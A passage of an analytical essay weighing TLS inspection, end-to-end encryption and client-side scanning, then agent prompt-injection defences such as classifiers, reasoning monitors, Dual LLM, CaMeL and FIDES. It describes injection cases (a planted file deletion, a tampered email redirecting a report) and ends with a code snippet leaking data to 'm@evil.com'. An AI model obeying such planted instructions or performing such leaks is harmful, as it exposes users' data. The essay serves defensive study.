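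The researchers applied this test to 7.75 billion connections from three sources: Firefox's update servers in February 2016, a group of shopping sites in August and September 2015, and a sample of traffic to Cloudflare, which delivers web pages for other sites, in May 2016. They had no header for the update servers, but only certain versions of Firefox connect there, so they compared each opening message with the ones those versions send.

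They graded the security of each connection from A, equivalent to a modern browser's, to F, weak enough that an attacker on the network could break in and read it. They then compared the grade of the browser named in the header with the grade of the connection that reached the server.

| Source | Connections intercepted | Security reduced | Security increased | Severely broken |
|---|---|---|---|---|
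| Firefox updates | 4.0% | 65.7% | 0.0% | 36.8% |
| Shopping sites | 6.2% | 26.5% | 4.1% | 17.7% |
| Shopping sites, middleboxes only | – | 62.3% | 0.9% | 58.1% |
| Cloudflare, US networks | 10.9% | 45.3% | 14.0% | 16.0% |

The last three columns are shares of the intercepted connections. Earlier studies found that 0.2% and 0.4% of connections were intercepted, less than a tenth of the rates in this table. The Cloudflare rate is the least certain. The raw data suggested 31%, largely because automated programs often pretend to be browsers. The researchers reached 10.9% by removing suspicious traffic and keeping only large US networks that serve ordinary users.

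Antivirus software accounted for 58% of the intercepted shopping connections that the researchers could trace to a product, and corporate middleboxes accounted for 35%. But the middleboxes did more damage, as the third row shows.

In laboratory tests in early 2016, eleven of twelve corporate middleboxes weakened connections under their default settings, and five introduced severe flaws. Microsoft's product did not check websites' certificates, so an impostor could have posed as any site, and the employee's browser would have shown a valid certificate from the middlebox. Only Blue Coat's product earned an A. It copied the browser's list of encryption methods instead of substituting a worse one.

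### The defenders' reply

Defenders of inspection can answer that these faults belong to particular products, and that Blue Coat's result shows they can be avoided. Fortinet fixed a known weakness in September 2016, and A10 added a setup tool that recommended better encryption. Other manufacturers never replied, or told the researchers that customers were responsible for configuring the products securely. The products are also a decade old and predate TLS 1.3, so the percentages are poor evidence about equipment on sale today.

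Official US advice is similar. A March 2017 alert now hosted by the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA), *HTTPS Interception Weakens TLS Security*, tells organisations that need inspection to make sure their products validate certificates correctly. In November 2019 the National Security Agency issued an advisory, and CISA's *NSA Releases Cyber Advisory* (2019) encouraged administrators to apply it. The passage quoted in Schneier's *The NSA Warns of TLS Inspection* (2019) calls the risks "not inconsequential" but says that mitigations exist.

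One of those risks would remain even if the middlebox had no bugs. Every computer in the company trusts the middlebox's root certificate, so an attacker who gained control of the signing key could impersonate any website to those computers or sign malicious software that they would accept. Passive decryption avoids this danger because the browser still checks the server's real certificate, but the shared private key becomes another valuable target for attackers.

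A better reply is that network operators cannot always count on every user and device to take proper precautions. Kühlewind, Trammell and colleagues (2018) make this "argument for the middle" for places such as company networks in *Challenges in Network Management of Encrypted Traffic*, a report on a workshop of researchers and network operators. In such places, one well-maintained checkpoint may protect more people than security software on thousands of machines, some of them out of date or already infected. The drawback, they acknowledge, is that the checkpoint becomes a prominent target for attackers. They also want middleboxes to be visible to the endpoints and to act only when both endpoints' security policies allow it, which rules out silently substituting a certificate.

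Durumeric and colleagues measured damage to encryption but did not count the attacks that inspection stopped, so their study cannot show whether companies were worse off overall. It does show that boxes installed for security often weakened the connections they handled. Many of the products supported safer settings, and the researchers urge administrators to test their configurations.

### Screening what an agent reads

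The argument about untrustworthy endpoints applies more strongly to AI agents. A laptop has to be infected before it can be used against its owner, but an agent may only need to read a web page that contains malicious instructions. A model that has just taken in such instructions is poorly placed to detect the attack, so there is a good case for having an independent system inspect the page before the model reads it.

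A classifier usually does the inspection. When a tool returns a web page or an email, the harness withholds the text from the model while the classifier estimates how likely the text is to contain an injection. If the estimate exceeds a chosen threshold, the harness can discard the text, add a warning or ask the user. The Frontier Model Forum notes that developers train such classifiers on known injections and also apply them to the model's outputs and to its activations, the internal values it computes while processing text. A classifier on activations can look for signs of an attack in how the model processes a passage, but running one requires access to the model's internals.

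Screening is also useful after the text first arrives. According to the Forum, a malicious instruction can enter an agent's stored memory, spread to other agents and resurface long after its source is gone. A harness that can read those memories and messages has more chances to catch it. When the memories and messages are encrypted, as in Codex's summaries and delegated tasks, the customer can screen the text only when it first arrives.

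A classifier's performance is measured by its detection rate (the share of real injections it flags) and its false-alarm rate (the share of harmless texts it flags). Moving the threshold improves one rate and worsens the other. The Forum says many agent security issues still lack standard benchmarks, so two vendors' rates may come from tests of very different difficulty.

Even a classifier with good error rates can produce mostly false alarms, because most of what an agent reads is harmless. Suppose, for illustration, that one tool result in 10,000 contains an injection, and that a classifier detects 90% of injections with a false-alarm rate of 1%. In 100,000 results, it would catch nine of the ten injections and flag about 1,000 harmless texts, so fewer than one alarm in a hundred would be real. If the errors were independent, an agent that made 100 tool calls in a session would have a 63%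 chance of at least one false alarm (1 − 0.99^100). With a false-alarm rate of 0.1%, that chance would fall to about 10%, and about one alarm in twelve would be real.

If every alarm goes to a person, that person will soon learn to dismiss them. The Forum says human approval in general may create an "illusion of oversight" when users click through. A slower, more careful second check on flagged items, like the one Anthropic uses for tool calls in Claude Code, can remove many false alarms before anyone sees them, but it cannot catch injections that the first check missed.

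Adaptive testing and theoretical work both show that such filters have limits. The Forum advises developers not to rely on detection alone and to keep fixed restrictions on an agent's tools and actions, outside the model's control. This weakens the case for inspection but does not defeat it. A filter that stops nine attacks in ten is still worth having, provided nobody gives the agent more authority because of it.

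### Reading a model's reasoning

Developers also monitor the reasoning a model writes before it acts. The Forum describes auditors that inspect this reasoning for signs of prompt injection. Such a monitor usually also receives the user's request and the proposed action, and it looks for a goal the user never set.

A model's reasoning can show why it took an action when the action alone does not. In the case of the deleted `customers.csv`, a line in the subagent's reasoning such as "the page says to remove the customer file first" would point to a planted instruction, and a monitor that saw the line in time could stop the command. Anthropic's auto-mode classifier cannot use this evidence because it is designed to judge actions without seeing the model's reasoning.

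Inspection works only to the extent that the model writes down what leads it to act. A suspicious line is a good reason to stop an action, but an innocent-looking account is a weaker reason to allow one, because the model may have left out the real cause.

The other difficulty is that OpenAI can run a monitor on the full reasoning in Codex, but the customer cannot, because the customer holds only the ciphertext and at most a summary. A customer who wants independent oversight is therefore in roughly the same position as the banks after TLS 1.3, though the banks had the advantage of owning the servers.

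### Refusing whatever is unreadable

Under the strictest version of the inspection position, a safety layer by default blocks any message it cannot read. Kühlewind and colleagues quote a workshop participant who said of networks, "If you can't understand a flow, then you should block the traffic."

Blocking content that a filter cannot read closes the simplest way around the filter, which is to encrypt the harmful part. Mistakes are also easier to spot, because people complain when a legitimate message is blocked but may not notice when a harmful one gets through. The rule also gives customers leverage, because suppliers who want their traffic to pass have a reason to make it readable. ETSI appealed to this pressure when it warned that companies might block TLS 1.3.

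The rule guarantees only that the inspector had a chance to read each message. It does not guarantee that the inspector understood the message or that the sender was entitled to make the request. Hardy's compiler would have satisfied the rule, because the name of the billing file was legible.

On networks, the rule has mostly hurt new protocols and extensions. Kühlewind and colleagues describe companies that block unfamiliar protocols or strip out unknown extensions, which forces connections back to older behaviour until the security equipment can handle the new features. QUIC, for example, is a newer transport protocol that encrypts information older ones leave exposed. Blocking it appeared harmless in 2018 because browsers fell back to the older TCP, but an application that worked only over QUIC would have stopped working. Protocol designers who expect such treatment have to imitate old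 traffic to get through, and improvements arrive late or not at all.

Encrypting more of a connection's metadata can also lead to more inspection. Firewalls have used the name of the requested website, which browsers traditionally send unencrypted, to let harmless connections through without decrypting them. They could check that name against the server's certificate until TLS 1.3 encrypted the certificate. Kühlewind and colleagues warn that a firewall that can no longer see or trust the name may have to decrypt every connection. A strict rule against exposing metadata would then leave employees with less privacy than before if their company insists on inspection.

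A harness that applied the rule to Codex would interrupt ordinary work almost at once. It would drop the model's encrypted reasoning, so the model would have to continue without it. It would reject the encrypted summaries that let a long session continue past the model's input limit. It would also block delegated tasks wherever Codex encrypts them, leaving the developer with a single agent or a model whose tasks remain readable. Outside the model's own traffic, the rule would block password-protected archives and many compiled programs, including some that developers install every day.

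Few organisations would accept all of that, so they would make exceptions, most likely starting with ciphertext that comes from the model's provider and goes back to it. A company that handles medical records may still find the stricter rule worthwhile for a small number of sessions with a single agent, readable tasks and no outside downloads. A programmer fixing a website would probably abandon the rule in the first long session.

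## The case for hiding content from every intermediary

A relay that can read a message can also leak it, alter it or hand it to someone who demands it. Privacy advocates, many cryptographers and the makers of encrypted messaging apps therefore want relays to be unable to read messages and to leave any checks to the sender and the recipient. They draw on an engineering argument from the early 1980s and on the experience of messaging companies, which have had to deal with abuse in conversations they cannot read.

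### The end-to-end argument

The engineering argument comes from Saltzer, Reed and Clark (1984), in *End-to-End Arguments in System Design*. Their main example is a program that copies a file from computer A to computer B:

1. The program's first half, on A, reads the file from A's disk.
2. It gives the file to the communication software, which splits it into packets.
3. The network carries the packets to B.
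4. Communication software on B passes the data to the program's second half.
5. The second half writes the file to B's disk.

The network may lose or change packets at step 3, but the file can also be damaged elsewhere. A disk may return wrong data, software may copy data incorrectly, memory may fail briefly, and either computer may crash. Even with a perfect network, the program would need its own protection against these faults.

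Saltzer and colleagues recommend checking the whole transfer. A stores the file with a checksum, a short number computed from the file's contents. After step 5, B reads its new copy back from the disk, recomputes the checksum and sends it to A. If the two checksums match, the copy is complete; if not, the program tries again. This check also catches the network's errors, so a more reliable network saves some retries but does not make the result more correct.

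Files were damaged on a network at MIT that lacked such a check. The network verified packets as they travelled between gateways, but not while they sat in a gateway's memory. One faulty gateway swapped two bytes about once in every million bytes. Programmers had assumed that the network was reliable, and they repeatedly sent an operating system's source files through this gateway. The owners of the damaged files had to correct them by hand from old printouts.

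Checks along the way can still improve speed. If a network loses one packet in 100, a file of 100 packets arrives whole on about 37% of attempts (0.99^100), and a file of 1,000 packets on about one attempt in 23,000. Resending individual packets is then well worth doing, but the final check is still necessary.

Saltzer and colleagues apply the same reasoning to encryption. If the network encrypts the data, the application must trust the network with the keys. The data is also exposed on the receiving computer before it reaches the application. The application must still check for itself who sent the message. An application that does its own encryption solves all three problems.

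This argument shows that encryption by the network is not enough. Concluding that relays should never read anything requires a further premise, that relays are untrustworthy or may become so. The argument is also compatible with an imperfect filter in the middle, as long as nobody treats it as the final check.

A further limit, more important for security, is that endpoints may be untrustworthy. The two halves of the copying program are both designed to make the copy succeed, and the checksum shows definitively whether it did. People who exchange messages may want to harm each other, or may be committing a crime together. According to Rickard, in *The End-to-End Principle in System Design*, Clark acknowledged in a follow-up paper in 2000 that the internet had filled with users who might not have others' interests at heart. The 1984 paper already contains an exception for untrustworthy endpoints.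 It suggests that a network might encrypt all traffic automatically, so that a misbehaving program cannot deliberately send out unencrypted information. The paper calls the end-to-end argument a guideline and "not an absolute rule".

### Private messaging

End-to-end encryption puts the argument into practice by letting only the communicating devices decrypt messages. Each user's app creates a pair of keys, publishes one and keeps the other on the device. The sender's app uses the recipient's public key to set up a secret that the two devices share, and the provider's servers carry only ciphertext. An intruder, a dishonest employee or a government that gains access to those servers gets delivery information but can't read the messages. To read them, an attacker has to break into phones, and each phone exposes only its owner's conversations.

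The provider still has one way to read messages, because it usually runs the directory of public keys. It could give the sender its own key in place of the recipient's and intercept the messages, as a TLS middlebox does with its substitute certificate. Messaging apps let users detect this by comparing a short code, but the check only works if users do it.

Encryption protects vulnerable people as well as criminals. The European Parliament's *Temporary derogation from the ePrivacy directive* (2026) is meant to let providers scan messages for child sexual abuse, yet its recitals, or explanatory notes, describe end-to-end encryption as important for the security of users, including children, and warn that malicious third parties could exploit any weakening. They also state that victims of abuse need confidentiality to communicate safely with a trusted adult or a lawyer.

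Providers may also have self-interested motives. Abelson, Anderson and colleagues (2021) note in *Bugs in our Pockets* that a company has far less content to moderate if it cannot see its users' messages, and that Facebook alone had 15,000 human moderators.

### Scanning before encryption

Client-side scanning is an attempt to keep encryption and still detect illegal content. The user's own device checks a message before encrypting it or after decrypting it.

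The method grew out of scanning on servers. A provider chooses a perceptual hash function and shares it with an organisation that holds verified abuse images, such as the National Center for Missing and Exploited Children in the United States. Unlike an ordinary hash, a perceptual hash stays nearly the same when somebody resizes or re-encodes a picture. The organisation returns a list of hashes of its images, so the provider never has to possess them. The server then compares each upload with the list, and a human may review possible matches before anyone reports them.

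Client-side scanning moves the comparison to the phone. If the system finds a match, it reveals the match, and possibly the user's identity, to the provider or the authorities. Otherwise, little or no information leaves the device. In August 2021 Apple proposed a version that would have checked only photos being uploaded to iCloud, using cryptography to prevent leaks about other pictures.

Perceptual hashing finds only close copies of known images. A machine-learning classifier can recognise new images. It usually works better on text, including messages used for grooming, in which an adult approaches a child for sexual purposes. Both methods sometimes flag innocent material.

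Supporters of scanning have a strong reason for not relying on users' complaints. When two offenders exchange abuse images, neither will report the other, and the child in the picture is not part of the conversation. The European Parliament's text credits voluntary scanning with helping to identify and rescue victims, limit the spread of the material and investigate offenders. Agence Europe's *Europol fears a sharp slowdown in investigations into online child sexual abuse* reports that in March 2026 Europol's head, Catherine De Bolle, was gravely concerned that the legal basis for such scanning would soon end. Her warning was a forecast about services where the provider can already read messages. But when such a service adopts end-to-end encryption, some detections are lost. If those detections matter, that is a reason to use client-side scanning, which could restore them.

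Abelson and 13 other computer security researchers reject this compromise. They call client-side scanning "bulk intercept, albeit automated and distributed", because it searches everyone's content, whether or not they are suspected of anything. Unlike antivirus software, which examines files on the user's behalf, the scanner works against the user. It can also access stored files that the user never sent to anyone.

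Another objection is that the phone's owner cannot check what the scanner looks for. The owner sees only hashes and cannot tell which pictures they represent, so a government could have images of a protest added without the owner noticing. Abelson and colleagues argue that only policy would limit the scanner to abuse images, and that a software update could extend it beyond pictures. The EU had already included terrorism and organised crime in its discussions of encrypted evidence. Abelson and colleagues also warn that skilled offenders could alter files to escape detection, and that criminals or abusive partners could use the scanner against the phone's owner.

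Some of these objections are stronger than others. Better engineering might reduce evasion and errors, and outside auditors might vouch for the list. But no design can bind a future government, and expanding the list would require no new access to anyone's phone. Abelson and colleagues found no version that would help the police substantially without putting law-abiding people at undue risk. That conclusion depends on how one weighs the help to police against the risk, and people who put more weight on undetected abuse may disagree.

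### The EU dispute in late 2026

The EU's current message-scanning rules exempt end-to-end encrypted apps such as WhatsApp and Signal, according to Euronews' *EU temporarily extends controversial chat-scanning regime until 2028* (2026). The EU adopted these rules in July 2026, and they run until 3 April 2028. They replace earlier temporary rules, which let providers scan messages voluntarily and lapsed on 3 April 2026.

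The exemption covers communications to which end-to-end encryption "is, has been or will be applied". Client-side scanning examines a message just before encryption, so the words "will be" seem to leave it without a legal basis under the temporary rules too. For unencrypted messages, a person must confirm any suspected grooming or previously unknown abuse material before the provider reports it. Text-scanning technology may look only for patterns that point to abuse and must not be able to determine what a conversation is about.

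The dispute now concerns the permanent regulation, which critics call Chat Control. The European Commission's 2022 proposal covered encrypted content. *Encryption and the scope of voluntary scanning in the EU's Chat Control* (2026), a digest by the anoni.net community, reports that negotiators had provisionally agreed to exclude it by June 2026. The digest also describes a leaked German diplomatic cable of 18 November, according to which at least nine countries wanted providers to be free to search unencrypted messages for known images, new images and grooming. France presented the exclusion of encrypted content as a concession to the Parliament. Spain's representative mentioned more than 1,000 abuse videos that campaigners had found on TikTok. That example supports scanning services the provider can read but has little bearing on encrypted ones.

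The European Parliament wants to limit searches to specific users and require a judge's approval, Rudl (2026) reports in *EU-Rat will für mehr Überwachung offenbar tricksen*. Rudl adds that the Council, which represents the member states, was apparently considering bypassing the Parliament's negotiators.

The provisional agreement then came into doubt. Reuter (2026), in *Zivilgesellschaft warnt vor Ausweitung der Überwachung*, reports that Ireland, which chairs the Council, proposed dropping the explicit protection for end-to-end encryption from the rules on voluntary scanning, according to a document leaked on 1 December. The German Bar Association warns that this could permit client-side scanning, which the protection rules out, though the proposal would not oblige any provider to scan. Breyer (2026), a longtime campaigner against the regulation, reports in *EU Governments to Greenlight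 Chat Control 2.0 Mass Scanning mandate* on an open letter from nearly 600 scientists against indiscriminate scanning.

The member states' ambassadors met on 2 December, and negotiators have scheduled a final round of talks for 8 December. Reuter thinks an agreement at that round is far from certain. If the talks fail, the temporary rules and their exemption remain in force until April 2028.

### Moderation without reading

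A provider can act against abuse without being able to read users' messages at will. In *Content-Oblivious Trust and Safety Techniques*, Pfefferkorn (2022) investigated what providers do in practice. She calls a technique content-dependent if the provider must be able to read users' messages and files at will, and content-oblivious if it need not. User reports are content-oblivious because the provider learns of the abuse only when somebody shows it to them.

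Between April and June 2021, Pfefferkorn sent a questionnaire to 58 people connected with more than 50 organisations. Her analysis covers 13 respondents from 11 of those organisations, including WhatsApp, with about two billion monthly users, and Lobste.rs, a link-sharing site with about 2,000. She asked which techniques they used and which worked best for each of 12 kinds of abuse.

| Technique | Must the provider be able to read content at will? | Respondents who use it (of 13) |
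|---|---|---|
| Reports made inside the app | No | 12 |
| Reports from outside the service | No | 10 |
| Human review of content | Yes | 10 |
| Metadata | No | 9 |
| Automated content scanning | Yes | 9 |
| Limits on group size | No | 7 |
| Limits on sharing or forwarding | No | 7 |

Metadata here means roughly the delivery information a relay can see, plus facts about the account. All nine providers that used it looked at internet addresses, account names and how often an account did something, and most also considered the account's age and earlier complaints. An hour-old account that messages 500 strangers looks like a spammer whatever it writes. The provider can block such an account or impose a rate limit, a cap on how many messages it can send in a given time. Limits on forwarding and group size slow the spread of harmful messages without identifying them, but they also slow popular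 harmless messages.

Respondents ranked user reports as the most useful way to detect nine of the 12 kinds of abuse, including harassment, hate speech and terrorism. Automated scanning ranked far ahead of reports for child sexual abuse images, and the two tied for grooming and other sexual exploitation of children. Among the nine providers that scanned content, scanning also ranked first for child sexual exploitation and for phishing and malware. This suggests that some respondents in the wider group preferred reports partly because they had no scanner.

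These results support encryption for most kinds of abuse, but they support child-protection campaigners on the kind those campaigners care about most. The evidence is thin. Pfefferkorn found many respondents through professional contacts. Most respondents were large American services, and they described their own practices. The questionnaire did not define "most useful", and it could not measure abuse that nobody detected. Pfefferkorn warns against generalising the results to all providers.

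The survey also found a gap in user reporting that providers could close without changing encryption. Of the 12 respondents with reporting tools in their apps, 11 said that users could report spam specifically, but only eight said that users could do so for child sexual abuse images.

### Message franking

When a provider cannot read messages, a recipient could invent an abusive message and report it as somebody else's, and the provider would have no copy to check it against. Pfefferkorn notes that providers can authenticate reports even in encrypted services. One way is message franking, which Facebook introduced in 2016 for encrypted chats in Messenger. It relies on HMAC, a standard function that turns a secret key and a text into a short tag.

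1. **Commitment.** The sender's app picks a random key `k` and computes `c = HMAC(k, m)` for the message `m`. It encrypts `m` and `k` together for the recipient and attaches `c` outside the encryption.
2. **Stamp.** The provider cannot work out `m` from `c`. It joins `c` to the sender's name, the recipient's name and the time, computes a second tag `t` from them with its own secret key, and forwards everything.
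3. **Check on arrival.** The recipient's app decrypts `m` and `k`, recomputes `c` and discards the message if the result differs.
4. **Report.** To complain, the recipient sends `m`, `k`, `c`, `t` and the delivery details to the provider, which recomputes both tags.

If both tags match, the provider knows that this account sent this message to this recipient. The recipient cannot substitute another message, because finding one that produces the same `c` is computationally infeasible, and cannot forge `t` without the provider's key. The provider learns nothing about the content until somebody complains.

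Without the check at step 3, an abuser could attach a meaningless `c`, and the victim would see the message but be unable to prove anything. Even with the check, the proof convinces only the provider, which holds the key for `t` and could have made the tag itself, so a court would have to take the provider's word. The recipient also chooses which messages to reveal and can leave out the provocation that came before. The main limit is that the scheme depends on somebody complaining.

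### Liability for a blind carrier

The "mere conduit" rule in Article 4 of the EU's Digital Services Act can protect a company from liability for messages it forwards for users but cannot read. The rule applies if the company does not initiate the transmission, choose the receiver, or select or modify the information. It also covers brief automatic storage along the way. Courts and authorities can still order the company to stop or prevent an infringement, but Article 8 bars governments from imposing a general duty to monitor what it carries.

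The conditions concern what the carrier does with a message, so a carrier that can read its traffic may still qualify. A carrier that chooses who receives a message fails the conditions even if the message is encrypted. Encryption makes the third condition easier to satisfy, since a company without the key can hardly select messages by their content or rewrite them. A hosting service, which stores users' material for longer, comes under Article 6 and can lose its protection if it knows of illegal content, for example from a user's report, and does not act promptly.

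Agent platforms fit Article 4 poorly. When a company's model writes a task and sends it to a subagent, the company's own system may have started the transmission, chosen the receiver and written the text. Article 4 protects carriers of information that users provide, so encrypting the task would not make the company a mere conduit. A service that only relays messages between different customers' agents would have a better claim to that protection.

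### When the endpoint is a model

Encrypted messaging relies on the recipient to read a message and then decide what to do about it. An agent may instead obey what it decrypts. If an encrypted email contains a hidden instruction, the attack arrives intact because no relay can detect it. Encryption still stops the relays themselves from reading secrets or planting instructions, which is a benefit when an agent's messages pass through several companies.

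A recipient's AI assistant may also read a decrypted message and send it to an AI company without the sender's knowledge, as Nabil Benamar, a professor at Moulay Ismail University, points out in CircleID's *AI Agents and the End of Endpoint Privacy*. In July 2025, for example, Google gave its Gemini assistant access to WhatsApp on Android by default. Meredith Whittaker, the president of Signal, warned in October 2026 of "the elimination of the possibility to provide privacy as an independent application developer". Benamar wants such access off until the user agrees, which protects the user but not the people who write to them. Running the model on the device, or in secure hardware designed for private processing, would keep the text from the AI company, but the model could still follow instructions in it.

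Some methods of blind moderation work better for agents than others. A rate limit can stop a hijacked agent from sending thousands of emails, just as it can stop a person, but one message may be enough to leak a password. User reports work poorly because they depend on a recipient who recognises abuse and objects to it, and a model that has accepted a planted instruction is unlikely to do either. Franking could help investigators if ordinary software running alongside the model, rather than the model itself, kept the key `k` for each message. After an incident, that software could reveal a single message and prove that the agent had received it.

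Saltzer and colleagues warn designers to "use some care to identify the end points", and agents make this difficult. In Codex, the endpoints for delegated tasks are OpenAI's servers, but the user is the one who knows what the job was supposed to be. If a check belongs with whoever has the knowledge to perform it, the end-to-end argument supports letting the user read those tasks, not hiding them.

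The same reasoning allows a monitor at the endpoint. Kühlewind and colleagues say that inspecting content requires the trust of at least one endpoint, while changing it requires the trust of both. A program on the user's computer that screens decrypted messages before the agent reads them, and alerts only the user, meets the requirement for inspection. It also avoids the main complaint about client-side scanning because, like antivirus software, it serves the device's owner. But it can only screen messages whose plain text is available somewhere under the user's control before it reaches the model, so it could not screen Codex's encrypted tasks.

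## The case for keeping the deciding model away from untrusted content

Screening can miss an injection, and the agent then reads it. Some security researchers therefore prefer a design in which the model that chooses the actions never receives text from outsiders. The model refers to emails, web pages and files only by name, so an instruction hidden in one of them cannot reach it. It is meant to pass along content it cannot inspect, and ordinary software decides where that content may go. The design draws on two older ideas from computer security, capabilities and information-flow labels.

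### A capability in place of a file name

Hardy's remedy was to give the compiler capabilities instead of file names. Tymshare would have supplied a capability to the statistics file, and a customer who wanted debugging output would have supplied one to the file that should receive it. The compiler would then have written each output using the capability supplied for it.

Under this arrangement, the customer could not have overwritten the billing file. Typing its name would have had no effect, because the compiler would no longer have turned names into files, and a customer with no right to write to BILL would have had no capability to pass on. The compiler could therefore no longer have combined a customer's choice of file with its own permission. Hardy had feared that capabilities would use up most of a system's storage, but he reports that the systems his company built on them were usually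 smaller than comparable ones, because capabilities replaced so many other mechanisms.

Capabilities alone do not protect an AI agent from injected instructions. An email assistant needs the rights to read the inbox and send messages, and an injected instruction can work by changing how the assistant uses those rights, without gaining any new ones. Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, formally define what it means for a program to be free of confused-deputy attacks and relate that definition to information-flow integrity, which limits what untrusted data may influence.

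### Two models and a controller

The programmer Simon Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", proposed a way to limit that influence in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). A privileged model takes the user's request and can use tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools, because Willison assumes it might "go rogue at any moment". A controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and stores the results. A request to summarize the latest email goes as follows:

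1. The privileged model asks for the email. The controller fetches it, stores it as `$VAR1` and tells the model only that name.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model asks the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user, and the controller fills in the text.

If the email contains an instruction to delete the inbox, the quarantined model may try to follow it, but it has no tool for deleting anything. The privileged model, which does have that tool, never receives the instruction. Willison's one exception is that the quarantined model may pass back a choice from a fixed list of categories, since the controller can check that the answer is on the list.

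Willison called this proposal "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use. If a single programming mistake lets untrusted text reach the privileged model, the protection is lost. An attacker might also use a manipulated summary to persuade the user to paste private data into a website.

### CaMeL

In *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind pointed out another weakness: an attacker can change a value even when every step follows the user's plan. Willison (2025) retells their example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's email address is in a file of meeting notes. An attacker who can plant text in the notes gets the quarantined model to return a different address. The controller stores this address as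 a variable, and the privileged model sends the document there.

Their system, CaMeL, keeps the two models and adds a way to track and check such values:

- **Plan.** The privileged model turns the request into a short program in a restricted form of Python before any tool runs.
- **Interpreter.** Purpose-built software runs the program, calls the tools and keeps track of which values each new value came from.
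- **Labels.** Each value carries tags for its source and its permitted readers.
- **Policy check.** Before each tool call, the interpreter applies the policy for that tool, which is a Python function, as *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains. A policy might let `send_email` proceed only if the recipient's address is trusted, and ask the user otherwise.

CaMeL stands for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning", but its "capabilities" are tags on data, not references like Hardy's.

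The design can also protect privacy. The planner receives only the user's request, so a company could run a large planner in the cloud and a smaller quarantined model on the user's computer. The cloud provider would then never receive the user's documents.

### Labels and how they spread

A few weeks after CaMeL, Microsoft researchers introduced a system called FIDES. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) defines its information-flow labels mathematically. These labels are tags that follow data through a computation and record where it came from or who may see it. FIDES uses an integrity label, which is either trusted (`T`) or untrusted (`U`), and a confidentiality label, which is the set of people who may read the data.

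A result inherits the restrictions of all its inputs. If a computation produces `z` from `x` and `y`, then

`label(z) = label(x) ⊔ label(y)`

The join of two labels, written `⊔`, is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. For integrity, `T ⊔ U = U`, so one untrusted input makes the result untrusted. For readers, the join is the intersection of the two sets, so `{Ana, Ben, Carl} ⊔ {Ben, Carl, Dee} = {Ben, Carl}`. Only people who may read both sources may read a document that combines them.

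Anything in a language model's context might affect its answer, so the answer inherits the label of the whole conversation. A single untrusted email in the conversation makes every later action untrusted. FIDES avoids this by hiding such text from the planner. Unlike CaMeL's planner, which writes the whole program in advance, FIDES's planner chooses one action at a time:

1. A tool returns a result with a label on each field.
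2. FIDES shows the planner the fields whose labels are no stricter than the conversation's. It stores the others in variables and shows the planner only their names.
3. The planner proposes a tool call, which may include variables as arguments.
4. FIDES replaces each variable with its content and looks up the label.
5. FIDES checks the call against the tool's policy. A *trusted-action* policy requires the decision to make the call, and any argument that matters, to carry the label `T`. A *permitted-flow* policy requires `recipients ⊆ readers(data)`, which means that everyone who receives the data must be among its permitted readers.
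6. If the call passes, the tool runs. Its result gets the join of the labels on the call, the arguments and whatever data the tool read.

Sometimes the planner cannot continue without knowing what a variable contains. It can read the content, but the conversation then becomes untrusted. It can also ask a quarantined model about the content and restrict the form of the answer. A yes-or-no answer gives an attacker one bit of influence, which is too little to carry an instruction, so a policy may allow it.

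### A tampered email

Suppose a user asks an assistant to "send the report to the address in Ana's email". Somebody has tampered with the email, replacing Ana's address with their own and adding a request to forward the whole inbox. A CaMeL-style planner, which has seen only the user's sentence, might write this program:

```
email   = get_latest_email(sender="Ana")
address = ask_quarantined("Which address does she give?", email, type="email address")
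report  = read_file("report.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=report)
```

| Step | What the attacker can change | Label on the result |
|---|---|---|
| Write the program | Nothing | Trusted |
| Fetch Ana's email | The text of the email | Untrusted |
| Extract the address | The address | Untrusted |
| Read the report | Nothing | Trusted; readers are the user and Ana |
| Send the report | The destination, if the policy allows it | – |

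The request to forward the inbox fails because the program has no step that forwards anything. The quarantined model may read the request, but it has no tools and can return only an email address. The attacker cannot change which file the assistant reads or how many messages it sends. The attacker can change only `address`, and with the Dual LLM pattern alone, the assistant would send the report to whatever address the attacker chose.

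A trusted-action policy stops the last step because `address` is untrusted, whether or not anyone has altered the email. The label records where the address came from, not whether it is correct. A permitted-flow policy compares the address with the report's list of readers, so it accepts Ana's real address and rejects the attacker's. If the assistant needs to satisfy only one of the two policies, it can take the last step without asking the user when the email is genuine, but not when it has been altered.

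This outcome depends on the list of readers. If the report is public, the permitted-flow policy lets it go anywhere. If Ana has a new address, the policy stops a legitimate message, and the user has to judge whether the address is hers. The attacker could also insert the address of somebody else who is allowed to read the report. The report would then reach the wrong person without breaking the policy.

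### Noninterference

The standard guarantee for a system of labels is noninterference. Write `x ~ₙ y` if two sets of inputs, `x` and `y`, agree in every part whose label is no more restrictive than `n`. A program `P` is noninterfering if, for every label `n`,

`x ~ₙ y ⇒ P(x) ~ₙ P(y)`

If `n` is "trusted", two runs that differ only in their untrusted inputs must produce the same trusted results. In the example, the program is such a result, because it is the same whatever Ana's email contains. If `n` is "public", changing a secret must not change anything the public can see.

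FIDES guarantees a weaker property called explicit secrecy. If `g` is the combined effect of one particular sequence of tool calls on stored data, explicit secrecy requires `x ~ₙ y ⇒ g(x) ~ₙ g(y)`, with `n` again "public". This covers what the calls do with secret data but not what an observer can infer from the choice of calls. For example, an agent that writes to a landlord only when the user's bank balance is high reveals something about the balance by writing. Costa and colleagues accept this gap because full noninterference would in effect forbid any publicly visible action once the agent had used a tool that might read a secret.

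CaMeL tracks some of these indirect leaks, but Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found a case that gets past it. A program along these lines shows the problem:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, the first test sets `tmp` to false and marks it secret. The line that would change `rich` therefore does not run. CaMeL updates a variable's label only when an assignment runs, so `rich` stays public and the email goes out. The recipient can infer from its arrival that the balance is high. An honest planner is unlikely to write such a program, so the flaw weakens the guarantee more than it weakens everyday security.

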